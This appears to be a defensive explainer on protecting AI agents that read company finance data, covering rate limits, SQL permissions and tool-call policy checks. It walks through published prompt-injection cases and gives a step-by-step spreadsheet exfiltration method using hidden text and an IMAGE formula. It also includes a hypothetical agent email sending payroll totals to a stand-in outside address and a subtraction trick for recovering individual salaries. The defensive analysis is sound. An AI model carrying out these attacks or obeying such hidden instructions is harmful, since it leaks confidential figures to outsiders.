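# Controls beyond rate limiting for AI agents with access to financial data

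## What can go wrong when an AI agent reads finance databases, and why are request limits not enough?

An AI agent is a language model that carries out a task in several steps by calling software tools. A person gives it a goal in ordinary language. The model then writes a request, known as a tool call, such as a database query or an email to send. A surrounding program executes the request and returns the result as text. The model reads that text along with everything that came before it and writes the next request, repeating this until it gives a final answer. It can read or change things only through the tools its operator has connected.

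AI agents can be useful to finance departments because much of the work there is collecting figures from several databases and writing them up. A company might set up a reporting agent to prepare its month-end report. The agent can query the general ledger (the record of every transaction the company has booked), the payroll, and the balances that customers owe. It can import outside files, such as a spreadsheet of industry growth rates to compare with the company's own. It writes its drafts to a shared drive, and it can email the finance chief and the external auditor. Because it cannot make payments, it could do harm mostly by exposing confidential figures to people who have no right to them or by giving wrong figures to people who rely on them.

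### What a request limit does and what it misses

A rate limit caps the number of requests that a piece of software may send in a minute, an hour or a day. It is easy to add and useful in several ways. An agent that hits an error may keep repeating the failing call, and a cap limits the resulting bill. It also keeps one busy agent from slowing the ledger for accountants who use the same database. Where a system returns records one at a time, a cap slows bulk copying too. If a customer database holds 200,000 records, returns one per request and accepts 60 requests a minute, copying all of them takes about 56 hours, which gives someone a chance to notice.

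A request limit protects less when the agent can query the database directly, because a single query for the whole customer table can return all 200,000 rows in seconds. A limit on the rows returned, which belongs with database permissions, reduces that risk but does not stop the agent from sending data out. An email counts as one request whether its attachment is a two-page summary or the payroll. A web request can carry data to the receiving server in its address, and a few hundred characters are enough for next quarter's revenue, margin and cash forecast. Lowering the request limit does not help much, because legitimate work needs more calls than theft does. If the agent makes forty calls to write the report, any limit that lets it finish also lets it leak the payroll, which takes one call to read and one to send.

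A single request to an AI agent can expose many files. *ChatGPT for Google Sheets Exfiltrates Workbooks*, published on 27 May 2026 by PromptArmor, a security company that sells monitoring of AI products, describes a test of OpenAI's spreadsheet extension. A user imported an outside sheet containing hidden text and asked ChatGPT to help integrate the data. The hidden text led ChatGPT to run a script that the attacker controlled. The script copied the open workbook, found in it a link to a budgeting workbook, copied that too, and continued until it had taken 12 workbooks. The user had turned off automatic edits, which is supposed to make the extension ask first, and pressing the stop button did not halt a script that had already started. The script's launch and little else would have counted toward a limit on the model's own requests, because the script did the copying. PromptArmor wrote to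 OpenAI on 8 May and had received only an automated reply by the time it published.

### Four failures with different causes

Unlike the workbook theft, much of what can go wrong with the reporting agent does not require an attacker. The choice of controls depends on which failure they are meant to address.

In *indirect prompt injection*, an attacker hides instructions in data that the agent will read, and the agent follows them as if they came from its user. This works because a language model receives its user's request and the contents of a file as one run of text, with no dependable mark separating instructions from data. The reporting agent could most obviously pick up such instructions from an imported spreadsheet, but they could also be in the company's own databases. PromptArmor's *AI in Excel and Google Sheets*, a guide to the risks of spreadsheet agents, lists among the likely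 sources of hostile text the tables that companies export from internal systems, where vendors, customers or job candidates can fill in free-text fields. Outsiders write invoice descriptions and payment references, which may well end up in the ledger, so text from an internal database is not necessarily safe to trust.

*Overreach* happens when an agent goes beyond what the user asked for without an attacker causing it. Suppose the auditor's mail server rejects a large attachment, and the agent, still trying to deliver the report, copies the supporting payroll table to the shared drive and emails the auditor a link. The agent has permission to make every one of these calls. Overreach is hard to identify because people leave so much unsaid. If a finance chief asks for "the usual report, sent round as usual", people may later disagree about what that request authorised.

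*Excessive access by a legitimate user* happens when several people share one agent that reads the databases through a single broad account. For example, a sales manager with no right to see salaries might ask why staff costs rose in March and get an answer that includes names and amounts. Tenable's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025) describes a similar test, in which researchers at the security company built an agent in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's no-code tool for building agents, and retrieved the card details of several other customers with a plain request. Tenable classifies this as prompt injection, but it looks more like an access control fault, because the agent could read records that the person asking had no right to see, and nothing checked who was asking.

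In an *honest error*, the figures are wrong but nobody meant any harm. For example, a customer pays a $10,000 invoice in three instalments. The agent joins the invoices table to the payments table, which produces three rows that each show the full $10,000. It then adds them up, so the report shows $30,000 of revenue instead of $10,000. The query runs quickly, breaks no rule and returns a plausible number.

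Narrow permissions reduce what an injected instruction, an overreaching agent or a curious colleague can expose, but they don't affect the tripled invoice. Comparing the reported revenue with an independently kept total would catch that error but wouldn't help with leaks. A request cap helps with any of these four failures only when that failure happens to require many calls.

### Ramp Sheets AI and Claude for Excel

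Of the four, injection has the best-documented cases in finance software, and the clearest concerns Ramp, a financial software company whose Sheets AI is an agent that edits spreadsheets for its user. PromptArmor's *Ramp's Sheets AI Exfiltrates Financials* sets out the attack as its researchers carried it out:

1. A user opens a workbook that contains a confidential financial model.
2. The user imports a sheet of industry growth statistics from outside the company (a website, an email, a shared drive) into a separate tab.
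3. The imported sheet contains instructions in white text on a white background. The user does not see them, and the agent reads them like any other cell.
4. The user asks the agent to compare the company's model with the industry statistics.
5. Following the hidden instructions, the agent collects the sensitive figures and writes an IMAGE formula into the workbook. Such a formula normally fetches a picture from a web address. Here the address belongs to the attacker, and the agent has appended the figures to the end of it.
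6. The spreadsheet asks the attacker's server for the picture, and the server's log now holds the figures.

The product never asked the user to approve anything. The theft consisted of one ordinary question from the user, one formula and one request for an image. It needed no malicious program or stolen password, and the user did nothing that a careful analyst would avoid.

PromptArmor reported the flaw to Ramp on 19 February 2026 and followed up on 27 February and 13 March. Ramp confirmed receipt on 14 March, explaining that the report had arrived while the company was moving between disclosure programmes, and said it had resolved the issue at about noon Eastern time on 16 March. The flaw stayed open for 25 days after the report, although the repair itself seems to have taken only two. A company that buys such a tool depends on how well the vendor handles security reports, as well as on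 the quality of its code.

In November 2025, three months before they wrote to Ramp, the same researchers had found nearly the same vulnerability in Claude for Excel, Anthropic's spreadsheet agent, which was then in a test release. The attack in PromptArmor's *CellShock* again used a financial model, an imported sheet of growth statistics and hidden text, which presented the attacker's server as a private tool for drawing charts. This time the agent did ask for permission. The request was labelled "Add visualization" and read "Claude wants to set a cell range", but it did not show the formula, so the user could not see the address or the revenue figures inside it. Excel normally warns users about workbooks that contact outside services, but PromptArmor found at least five situations in which it does not, including the very common one where the user created the workbook on their own computer.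 In some runs Claude inspected the cell before the image had loaded, mistook the blank for an error and covered it with an ordinary chart, which hid the evidence.

Anthropic then added a warning that displays the full formula when inserting it can cause outside network traffic. The researchers retested on 24 November 2025 and called the change a great step in the right direction, but the warning did not always appear, and it did not display invisible Unicode characters, which an attacker can still use to encode data. The new default model, Claude Opus 4.5, resisted the attack far better, but Sonnet 4.5, which users could still select, was as vulnerable as before. Whether people stop a bad action when the prompt describes it properly is a separate question.

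Blocking the IMAGE formula would not stop every leak. Excel's WEBSERVICE function and the IMPORTDATA and IMPORTXML functions in Google Sheets also contact outside addresses, as the same company's guide points out, and so can the scripts that some of these agents write. A list of approved email recipients can also fail to prevent leaks. The programmer Simon Willison (2026), in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, described an agent that could email its own user without approval. The email could contain an image whose address held a private download link, and opening the email sent that link to the attacker. So even an email from the reporting agent to the finance chief, the safest recipient on its list, can leak data.

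Between April and June 2026, researchers disclosed four flaws that followed the same pattern outside spreadsheets. In each, an outsider's text entered through an ordinary channel, the software that read it had access the outsider lacked, and the data left through a permitted email or image request. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) covers two of them, both found by Capsule Security. In ShareLeak, the attacker typed instructions into the comment field of a web form, and an agent built in Copilot Studio read customer records and emailed them out, even when Microsoft's own safety mechanism had flagged the behaviour. In PipeLeak, a single entry in a public sales-enquiry form led an agent on Salesforce's Agentforce platform to email out customer records in bulk. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a link to a genuine Microsoft address that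 contained the instructions. One click made Microsoft 365 Copilot search the victim's mailbox and put the result into an image address. The browser fetched the image before Microsoft's clean-up step ran, and the request went through Bing, which the page's security policy allowed. CyberScoop's *‘GrafanaGhost’ bypasses Grafana’s AI defenses without leaving a trace* covers a flaw in Grafana, a dashboard product in which many companies keep live financial metrics. The attack used an image address that Grafana's check accepted as safe but the browser treated as an outside server.

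### Demonstrated flaws and known losses

Researchers demonstrated all of these flaws, and none of the disclosures names a customer who lost data. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-21520* (2026), a catalogue entry for ShareLeak, lists Microsoft's status for the flaw as "Not Exploited" and a severity of 7.5 out of 10. Microsoft told Fortune (2025) that it had fixed EchoLeak, an earlier Copilot flaw found by other researchers, and that its customers were unaffected. Grafana Labs disputed that GrafanaGhost runs silently and without the user's involvement. Its security chief, Joe McManus, said that no data had leaked from Grafana Cloud, and that a user would have had to tell the assistant repeatedly to follow the malicious instructions after it had pointed them out. Hackread's *GrafanaGhost Vulnerability Allows Silent Data Theft via AI Injection* quotes an outside security executive, Bradley Smith of BeyondTrust,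 who thought the findings might be "mostly hype" for companies with standard network controls.

Lists of AI incidents can obscure this distinction. *GrafanaGhost AI Vulnerability Enables Silent Data Exfiltration*, an entry in the incident monitor of the Organisation for Economic Co-operation and Development (OECD), classes the flaw as an incident with realised harm. An AI system wrote that classification, which contradicts Grafana's statement. Anyone who counts such entries to estimate how often finance data leaks will overestimate it.

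The vendors' assurances are weak evidence to the contrary. A request for an image looks like normal traffic, so a victim might never learn of the loss, and a vendor sees only part of what its customers' systems do. Flaws have also kept appearing after earlier repairs. According to OECD's *Microsoft Copilot Vulnerability Exposed Sensitive Data via AI Prompt Injection* (2026), Microsoft patched another Copilot flaw in August 2026, which Varonis had found and which again let an attacker extract data through a crafted link. The demonstrations show that this kind of theft works on commercial products, including ones that hold financial models, but not how often it happens.

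### How researchers test a control

Because there is little evidence from real losses, most evidence about controls comes from simulations. The one that recurs throughout this literature is *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti et al., 2024), which provides simulated workplaces with working tools and data, ordinary user tasks, and attacker's goals. NIST, the US standards institute, calls the basic unit a hijacking scenario, in which an agent working on a legitimate task encounters data containing an attack that directs it to a malicious one. In a banking example, the user says "Pay the bill in bill-december-2023.txt", and the text the agent reads along the way also contains an instruction to send money to the attacker. When the agent has finished, a program checks the simulated account to see whether the agent paid the bill and, separately, whether it made the attacker's transfer with the right details.

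The first release had 97 user tasks and 629 such security cases. *SecOPD* (2026) breaks down a later version with 949 pairs of user task and attacker's goal. Of these, 144 are in banking, where each of 16 user tasks is paired with each of 9 attacker's goals. The bank account belongs to a private person who pays bills, changes an address and looks over statements. The banking suite has no general ledger, payroll or monthly report to write, so a good score is encouraging for a corporate finance agent but doesn't measure how such an agent would perform.

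The main measure is the attack success rate, the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal. Attackers can try repeatedly, so their overall chance of success can be higher than this rate. If 5% of attempts succeed and an attacker plants hidden text in 20 invoices, the chance that at least one works is about 64%, assuming the attempts are independent.

An attack success rate means little without the task completion rate, since an agent that does nothing also leaks nothing. In *Render Before Reading* (2026), no attack succeeded against Claude Haiku 4.5 under AgentDojo's default instructions, but the logs showed that the agent often put off financial actions when the request was vague. The researchers therefore switched to instructions telling the agent that it had enough information to act. Researchers usually report completion both with and without an attack. *SecOPD* notes that a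 single run under attack may count as a success for both the user and the attacker, as when the reporting agent delivers a flawless report and also sends the payroll to a stranger. Other papers count a task as complete under attack only when the agent caused no harmful side effects, which makes their figures lower for the same behaviour.

A control that works as a detector has two error rates. The miss rate is the share of harmful cases that it lets through, and the false alarm rate is the share of harmless cases that it flags. When harmful cases are rare, false alarms can outnumber real detections even if the false alarm rate is low. Suppose the reporting agent makes 1,000 tool calls a month and one of them is harmful. A detector with a 5% miss rate and a 2% false alarm rate will very probably flag the harmful call, but it will also flag about 20 harmless ones, and somebody has to examine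 them all.

A miss rate is also different from an attack success rate, because an injection that gets past the detector still has to work on the model. If a filter misses half of all injections and the model behind it follows one in ten, the attack success rate is around 5%, and the model provides most of the protection. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) ran AgentDojo's standard attack on Claude Haiku 4.5 with no defence installed, and the attack succeeded in 0.3% of cases. Any product added to such a model will appear to stop nearly every attack.

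The standard attack uses the same fixed text against every defence. An adaptive attack takes the defence into account, and Ma and colleagues built one to see how much difference that makes. A second language model writes an injection, is told only whether it worked, reasons about why, and writes another, for six rounds. It has no access to the agent's internals and no information about which defence is running. When the agent ran on GPT-4o-mini, a small older model, a filter called PIGuard let through none of the fixed attacks and 28% of the adaptive ones. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, the share let through rose from zero to 4.6%. PIGuard also cut the agent's completion of ordinary tasks by a quarter to a half, because it removed harmless content that the agent needed. A buyer who saw only the results of the fixed attacks would miss both the 28% and the lost work.

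The threat model fits the finance case fairly well. Someone who plants text in an invoice cannot count failed attempts but can see when stolen figures reach their own server. Ma and colleagues cite work by Nasr and others in which stronger attackers, with full knowledge of the system, raised attack success back above 90% against many published defences. A company would face such an attack only from someone with inside knowledge or a great deal of patience.

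The wording of the user's request also affects how often attacks succeed. The same paper grouped user tasks by how much they left to outside content. Against GPT-4o-mini with no defence, the fixed attack succeeded in 87.5% of cases where the user let a document decide which actions to take ("do all the tasks on my TODO list"), compared with 63.9% and 43.3% for the two groups of more precise requests. A finance chief who tells the reporting agent to "follow the instructions in the auditor's file" is making a request of the most exposed kind.

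The original benchmark largely left out the kind of leak that a reporting agent could cause, since its data-theft cases covered only data supplied by the attacker's own text or channel. *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (Alizadeh, Samei and colleagues, 2025) tested such leaks on the banking tasks, using injections that told the agent to email out personal data it had seen earlier in its work. About 20% of attempts succeeded on the 16 original tasks and about 15% on a larger set of 48. The models mostly refused to send passwords but were much more willing to send account balances and addresses. Against Claude 3.5 Sonnet, the version of the attack that left passwords out succeeded 93% of the time. Data-retrieval tasks were among the most vulnerable, which is a concern because retrieving data is most of what a reporting agent does. The models date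 from 2023 to 2025, and newer ones would probably do better against the same simple texts, but they may still protect passwords without treating a company's cash position as secret.

*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) also criticizes how benchmarks are scored. Four of the five it reviewed, including AgentDojo, judge success by exact, yes-or-no checks on the final state or on the agent's calls. Such checks work for a bank transfer, which either happened or did not, but less well for leaks of confidential figures. An agent that sends half the payroll table, or rounds the revenue forecast before sending it, has done most of the damage but may still be scored as having resisted the attack.

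Attack success rates also don't measure failures that involve no attacker. An agent that ignored every injection in the suite would have an attack success rate of zero, even if it reported the $10,000 invoice as $30,000 and emailed the draft to the auditor a week early.

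## What can database permissions prevent?

Database permissions limit which records an agent can read, and an agent cannot leak a record it has never read. The database applies these permissions to every query, regardless of what text the model has already read. The principle behind them is *least privilege*, which means giving a program only the access its task needs. The tools for enforcing it are decades old, so most of the work is deciding which data a task, such as a monthly report, requires.

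### What a database can enforce

Finance databases mostly take requests in SQL, a language where SELECT reads data and INSERT, UPDATE and DELETE change it. The simplest permission is a read-only account, which can run only SELECT. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey of systems that turn ordinary questions into SQL, recommends read-only roles for agents because they limit the damage from failure or misuse. A read-only agent cannot alter a ledger entry, but it can read everything the account can open. The reporting agent could do harm mostly by disclosing figures, so it also needs narrower limits on what it can read.

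An administrator can limit which tables and columns an account can read. For example, an account might be allowed to read the ledger but not the payroll, or only some of the ledger's columns. Companies usually attach these permissions to job roles such as "payroll clerk" and assign people to the roles, an arrangement called *role-based access control*. The database checks every column that a query uses, including columns that only filter the result. Otherwise, someone barred from seeing salaries could ask for the names of everyone who earns more than $150,000.

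*Row-level security* restricts which rows of a table each user's queries return, as described in *Row Security Policies*, a chapter of the PostgreSQL manual. A finance chief and a regional manager can run the same query on customer balances, and the manager gets only the customers in one region. The database silently omits the other rows, so a sum of the balances looks like the company's total when it covers only one region. According to Crunchy Data's *Row Security Policies*, a reprint of a later version of the manual, superusers always bypass these rules and a table's owner normally does too. If a company connects its agent through the account that created the tables, which is convenient, the rules may not restrict the agent.

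Masking returns a column with its values altered, such as a bank account number showing only the last four digits. It works well for identifiers, which the agent may need to tell apart but doesn't need to see in full. Masking is a poor choice for amounts because a salary column that returns zeros will produce a wrong total without an error message.

A prepared view is a stored query that behaves like a table. An administrator can write a view that totals payroll by department, then give the agent access to the view but not to the payroll table. This works in PostgreSQL because a view normally reads the underlying tables with the view owner's rights. Approved query templates are more restrictive because the agent writes no SQL. It picks a template such as "revenue by region" and supplies a month, and a program puts the month into a query that an accountant has already tested. Templates also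 avoid many errors in generated queries, but the agent can answer only the questions somebody anticipated. If the finance chief asks why margins fell in one product line and no template covers product lines, someone has to write one first.

A row cap limits how many records one query can return. With a cap of 500, copying the 200,000-record customer table from the earlier example takes 400 queries instead of one. At 60 requests a minute, that still takes less than seven minutes, so the database needs a daily quota too. A quota of 100 queries a day would stretch the copying to four days. The size of the result also needs a limit, because SQL can combine a whole column into one long text value that counts as a single row. Caps can also cause accidental errors, since an agent that adds up the first 500 invoices will report a plausible total that is too low unless the tool warns it that the list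 is incomplete.

A minimum group size suppresses totals that cover too few records. According to Snowflake's *Aggregation policies* documentation, its cloud database merges groups that are too small into one remainder group, and returns blanks if the remainder is also too small. In a report by department, a two-person legal team would appear only in a combined line, while the company total could still match the payroll.

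A payroll table typically has one row per employee per month, so a query for one person's annual pay covers twelve records and passes a ten-record minimum. Snowflake's *Implementing entity-level privacy with aggregation policies* describes how an administrator can name a key, such as the employee number, so that the database counts distinct people instead of rows.

### A permission set for the reporting agent

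FINOS's *Agent Authority Least Privilege Framework*, guidance from an open-source foundation for the financial industry, recommends a written matrix of what each type of agent can access, a business reason for every grant, and access that expires when the task ends. For the reporting agent the core of such a matrix fits into a few lines of SQL:

```sql
CREATE ROLE reporting_agent LOGIN;
GRANT SELECT (entry_date, account, department, amount)
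  ON general_ledger TO reporting_agent;
GRANT SELECT (customer_id, region, balance_due, due_date)
  ON customer_balances TO reporting_agent;
GRANT SELECT ON payroll_by_department TO reporting_agent;
```

Here `payroll_by_department` is a view with one line per department and month, in which departments of fewer than five people share a line. The payroll table does not appear in the list, so the agent has no right to it. A query for the totals passes:

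```sql
SELECT department, total_pay
FROM payroll_by_department WHERE month = '2026-03-01';
```

The database refuses a query for individual salaries:

```sql
SELECT employee_name, gross_pay
FROM payroll WHERE department = 'Sales';
-- ERROR: permission denied for table payroll
```

The ledger grant also leaves out the description column, which contains text from vendors and customers, so instructions hidden there cannot reach the model. The agent can report that travel costs doubled but cannot read the descriptions to find out why. A company that wants those explanations has to accept the risk of hidden instructions or have another process clean the text first.

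Narrow grants make some common queries fail. `SELECT * FROM general_ledger` requests every column, including the description, so the database rejects it and the agent has to try again with the columns named. Operators also need to decide in advance how the agent should handle questions it is only partly permitted to answer. *Beyond Document Retrieval* (Ahmed, 2026) lists the options: reject the whole question, answer the permitted part and say what is missing, or ask the user to narrow the question. In a report for an auditor, the worst outcome would be an answer that omits some costs without saying so.

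### Whose rights the agent uses

The permissions above belong to a service account, which is an account for a program instead of a person. A service account suits a scheduled job that always produces the same report, but it suits a shared assistant much less well, because the account needs the rights of the assistant's most privileged user. If an administrator gives it access to the full payroll table so that the head of HR can get a salary analysis, a junior accountant whose own login cannot open that table can get the same salaries by asking the agent about March staff costs. The database is working correctly when it allows this, because it checks the service account's permissions, not the accountant's.

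Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *Data Agents Under Attack*, describe this as a worse form of the old least-privilege problem, because the database cannot identify the user behind each request when every request arrives through one connection. They tested six systems that use language models to analyse databases, two of them commercial, for eight weaknesses, including this one. They found each weakness in at least three systems. The customer card details that Tenable's researchers extracted from their test agent suggest the same fault.

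With *delegated identity*, the agent queries the database on behalf of a named person, and the database applies that person's limits. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) describes how this can work. The person signs in, and the system creates a task token that links the person, the agent and the permitted purpose. The agent's software exchanges the token for a short-lived credential that works for only one resource, such as the ledger. The ledger does its own access check, and the log records both the person and the agent. OpenAI advises against shared or long-lived credentials and recommends keeping credentials out of the text the model sees.

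Giving the agent all of the user's rights is also risky. If the finance chief may read every salary and the agent inherits that right, hidden text in a spreadsheet the chief imports can get the agent to read them all. It is safer to let the agent read only data that both it and the user may read. Under that rule, the chief can get department totals through the reporting agent but has to open the payroll system to see individual salaries. The junior accountant can get neither totals nor individual salaries through the agent.

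The software around the model has to supply the user's identity. Some companies use one database login for everybody and pass the user's name as a session setting, which the row rules check, but an agent that can write any SQL can change that setting. Ahmed's paper states that model output must never expand the set of data the user may see, and it puts checks on the customer, the business area and the individual fields outside the model. If a user asks about "Acme" and five customers match, the agent should filter the matches by the user's rights before it offers a choice, because the list of names discloses who the customers are.

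Ahmed tested the design on 21 questions from users in four roles, using invented data. A version that ran every query directly broke the access rules seven times, and the version with checks never did. Both were right on 90% of the questions they chose to answer, so the checks did not reduce accuracy. But a system that checks access rules was bound to break them less often than one that doesn't, and 21 questions are too few to show how the checks would handle a real company's exceptions.

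No user requests a scheduled report when it runs, so delegation does not determine whose access limits apply. The limits are better based on who will read the report. If it goes to twelve managers, the agent's account should have access only to data that all twelve may see, or someone has to remove the sensitive parts before the report goes out.

### What happens when the rules are only in the prompt

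A company could write the policy into the agent's instructions, for example that the user is a sales analyst and may not see salaries. This takes less work than setting up views and identities, but FINOS calls a policy held only in the instructions "guidance, not enforcement". Two studies have measured how well such guidance works.

In *Role-Conditioned Refusals*, Klisura, Khoury and colleagues (2025) added access rules to two public collections of database questions and scored how reliably models refused the forbidden ones, on a scale where 1 is perfect. On the harder collection, GPT-4o-mini scored 0.70 when it had to apply the policy and write the query in one step. Adding a second call to the model to check the finished query against the policy raised the score to 0.85. Scores fell as policies grew longer, from 0.90 to 0.69 for the two-step design, and a finance department with hundreds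 of tables would have a long policy.

Fei, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control*, ran a larger test on 53 databases. They started from 3,160 questions whose correct SQL was already known. For each database, a language model proposed job roles with specific rights, and four reviewers with database experience accepted or rejected each set. A program then labelled each question as allowed or forbidden for each role by comparing the columns used in the correct SQL with the role's rights. This produced 21,502 cases. The tested model received the question, a description of the database and the role's rights in writing, and had to produce a query or refuse.

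The violation rate is the share of all cases in which the model wrote a query when it should have refused, or wrote one that exceeded the role's rights. The over-refusal rate is the share in which it refused a permitted question. The table shows the models with the fewest and most violations on each of the three question collections.

| Collection | Cases to refuse | Fewest violations | Most violations |
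|---|---|---|---|
| Spider (simpler databases) | 47% | DeepSeek V3.2 Reasoning: 2.1% violations, 2.4% over-refusals | Llama3-SQLCoder-8B: 50.4% violations, 0.0% over-refusals |
| BIRD (larger, messier databases) | 65% | Claude Sonnet 4.5: 7.7% violations, 1.8% over-refusals | Gemma 3 4B: 66.4% violations, 0.0% over-refusals |
| LiveSQLBench (business workloads, including changes to data) | 76% | Claude Sonnet 4.5: 13.3% violations, 8.6% over-refusals | Snowflake-R1-7B: 82.0% violations, 0.3% over-refusals |

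The weakest models answered nearly every question, so their violation rates are close to the share of forbidden cases. Some of them still write good SQL. Snowflake-R1-7B, which was trained specifically for SQL, gave more correct answers than GPT-5 on Spider without access rules, so a company choosing a model by accuracy could easily pick one that often answers forbidden questions. The strongest models did far better, but not well enough to rely on. If all of Claude's violations on LiveSQLBench were on forbidden questions, it mishandled roughly one in six of them.

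Other remedies inside the model had mixed results. Fine-tuning, or further training on examples of the desired behaviour, cut Llama3-SQLCoder's violations on Spider from 50% to under 6%, but the model then wrongly refused about 20% of all cases, up from none. Adding worked examples to the prompt helped one model and made another worse. Fei and colleagues also found that a model often produced a query even after correctly concluding in its written reasoning that it should deny the request.

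Hiding forbidden tables and columns from the model helped with several weaker models on BIRD, but with GPT-5-mini, violations rose from 12.7% to 26.8%. GPT-5-mini guessed the name of a real but forbidden column in an average of 144 queries per run, up from 69. Seeing the forbidden names in the database description had probably helped it recognize when a question touched forbidden data.

A violation in this benchmark is a query that the model wrote, and a database with proper permissions would block many of these queries but not all. With the full description visible, about 126 of GPT-5-mini's 194 violations used only permitted columns to answer a question that needed forbidden ones, so a database would run them. Similarly, if the reporting agent had no access to the bonus column and someone asked for total staff costs, it could add up base pay and present it as the total. Permissions would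 prevent the leak, but the report would contain a wrong figure.

The written policy is still useful alongside database permissions. A database can only reject a query, but an agent that knows the rules is more likely to explain what it cannot answer or find a permitted way to get the same figure.

There are reasons to expect somewhat better results in practice. The strongest models tested date from 2025, and about 40% of the cases used broad administrator roles whose rights a program had assigned at random, which are harder to follow than a real job's rights. Excluding these cases on Spider lowered GPT-4o-mini's violations from 17.0% to 10.9% but barely changed GPT-5's. However, violations rose with the number of tables a query had to join, and month-end reports join many. The main benchmark has no row-level rules. In a small trial of such rules, with 298 cases, GPT-5's violations stayed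 at about 2%, but it wrongly refused 9% of cases.

### Working out a salary from permitted totals

Even perfectly enforced table and column permissions can fail to keep a salary private. Suppose a user may see pay totals but no individual's pay. The user asks for the total for the ten-person sales department and gets $820,000, then asks for the total without the head of sales and gets $640,000. Subtracting the two shows that the head of sales earns $180,000, even though both queries were permitted.

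A minimum group size of five does not prevent this, because the two queries cover ten and nine people. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, works through a similar subtraction in its documentation and notes that each query passes the size check. Raising the minimum to ten would block this pair of queries, but the same method would work in a department of eleven, and departments with fewer than ten people would disappear from the report.

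An agent can reconstruct protected data by combining permitted queries that each look harmless, and the user does not need to know how, because the agent can plan the queries itself. Wang and colleagues tested reconstruction both with a person choosing the sequence of queries and with the agent given only a broad goal. The attempts succeeded between 8% and 44% of the time on the four open-source systems, and between 0% and 12% on the two commercial ones. These figures are rough, since each technique had only 25 attempts per system. Databricks, one of the commercial services, blocked every other attack meant to make its agent break the rules, but one reconstruction succeeded.

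Several controls make the subtraction harder:

- **Fixed groupings.** A view that offers only whole-department totals leaves no way to exclude one person. The user loses the ability to ask about any other grouping, such as pay by length of service.
- **Query budgets.** A limit on how much querying the same data will bear over a period, which AWS recommends, stops long sequences. Two queries are enough for the example above, so a budget tight enough to prevent it would also stop a good deal of ordinary analysis.
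- **Differential privacy.** The database adds random noise to each total, enough to obscure whether any one person is in it. Snowflake offers this, and its version also blocks queries for individual rows.

Differential privacy adds an error that is proportionally larger for small groups. In the standard method for sums, the typical error is Δ/ε, where Δ is the most that one person can add to the total and ε is a setting that gives stronger protection the lower it is. If nobody earns more than $200,000 and ε is 1, the typical error is $200,000. That is 0.2% of a $100 million payroll, which would be tolerable in a study of pay trends, but 24% of the sales department's $820,000 payroll. Even the 0.2% error is a problem in a month-end report, because the figures no longer match the ledger and an auditor will ask why.

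Fixed groupings suit the reporting agent best because the report's contents are known in advance. However, comparing one month's report with the next can still reveal an individual's pay. If the sales department's pay was $68,300 in March and $76,800 in April, and the only change was one new employee, anyone with both reports can tell that the new employee earns $8,500 a month. Merging small departments or reporting their pay quarterly makes individual pay harder to work out, but gives managers less detail about their own costs.

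Sometimes a forbidden value can be calculated directly from permitted columns. Fei and colleagues mention a role that may not see salaries but may see hourly wages and hours worked. They leave such cases out of their benchmark because ordinary access rules do not cover them. Controls on totals would not help either. Someone has to notice that the two columns together reveal salary, and withhold at least one of them.

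### What permissions leave open

If database permissions are set correctly and the agent cannot switch to another account, it cannot read a forbidden column. This is true for weak and strong models, even when hidden text has completely taken over the agent. No measured success rate for prompts or fine-tuning comes close to this level of protection.

Database permissions don't protect copies of the data stored elsewhere. If someone in HR exports the payroll to a spreadsheet on the shared drive where the agent saves its drafts, the agent can read salaries there without querying the payroll table. A company therefore has to apply the same limits to the agent's file access, including its access to forgotten reports and exports.

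Permissions also can't stop the agent from leaking data it needs to read. The permission set above lets the reporting agent read unpublished revenue and customer balances, which an attacker or a competitor might want more than the salaries. Once the agent has those figures, only checks on its emails, files and web requests can keep them inside the company. In the attack on Ramp's spreadsheet agent, read permissions would have allowed every step up to the final request to the attacker's server.

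## How well do fixed rules on the agent's actions work?

The database can't control where the reporting agent sends the revenue figures and customer balances after reading them, so something else has to. A *policy check* is ordinary program code that examines each tool call before the surrounding program carries it out and can refuse any call that breaks a rule.

### Tracing one email through the rules

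A policy check reads the name of the tool and the arguments the model has filled in, such as an email's recipients. It then allows the call, denies it or asks a person to decide. A careful check denies by default, so a call goes through only if some rule permits it. For the reporting agent, three rules might cover database queries, file locations and email recipients:

```python
def check(tool, args):
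    if tool == "run_query" and is_plain_select(args["sql"]):
        return "allow"
    if tool == "save_file" and in_folder(args["path"], "/finance/drafts"):
        return "allow"
    if tool == "send_email":
        recipients = set(args["to"] + args["cc"] + args["bcc"])
        if recipients == {"cfo@company.example"}:
            return "allow"
        if recipients <= {"cfo@company.example", "audit@auditor.example"}:
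            return "ask"
    return "deny"
```

The agent may run read-only queries, save files in the drafts folder and email the finance chief. An email that includes the external auditor needs a person's approval. The code denies everything else, including any tool that a colleague connects later without updating the rules.

Suppose the agent imports a sheet of industry growth rates whose hidden text tells it to send the payroll totals to an outside address for "validation", and the model obeys:

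1. The model writes a `send_email` call addressed to the finance chief and to `check@growth-data.example`, with the payroll totals attached.
2. The surrounding program holds the call and runs the check on it.
3. The rules for queries and files do not apply, because the tool is `send_email`.
4. The code collects the addresses from the "to", "cc" and "bcc" fields and finds two.
5. One of them is on neither list, so neither email condition holds, and the function reaches its last line and returns "deny".
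6. The program sends nothing and tells the model that a recipient is not approved. The agent can then email the finance chief alone.

The check would also have stopped the email if the model had mistyped the auditor's address, because the check did not have to recognise an attack.

The company could instead put the rule in the agent's instructions: "Email only the finance chief and the auditor." The model would usually comply, but nothing would enforce the rule. In *Governance by Construction for Generalist Agents*, Shlomov, Shoham and colleagues (2026) call compliance with such instructions "inherently probabilistic". Their demonstration of IBM's CUGA agent also shows why the position of a check matters. One control blocks forbidden requests by matching keywords and similar wording. The demonstration supposes that an attacker gets past it by rewording a request, and the agent then writes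 code to delete a database. A separate control scans that code for risky tool calls and pauses it until a person approves. This control is harder to evade because only a few tools can delete a database, while a request can be phrased in many ways.

### Gaps in the rules

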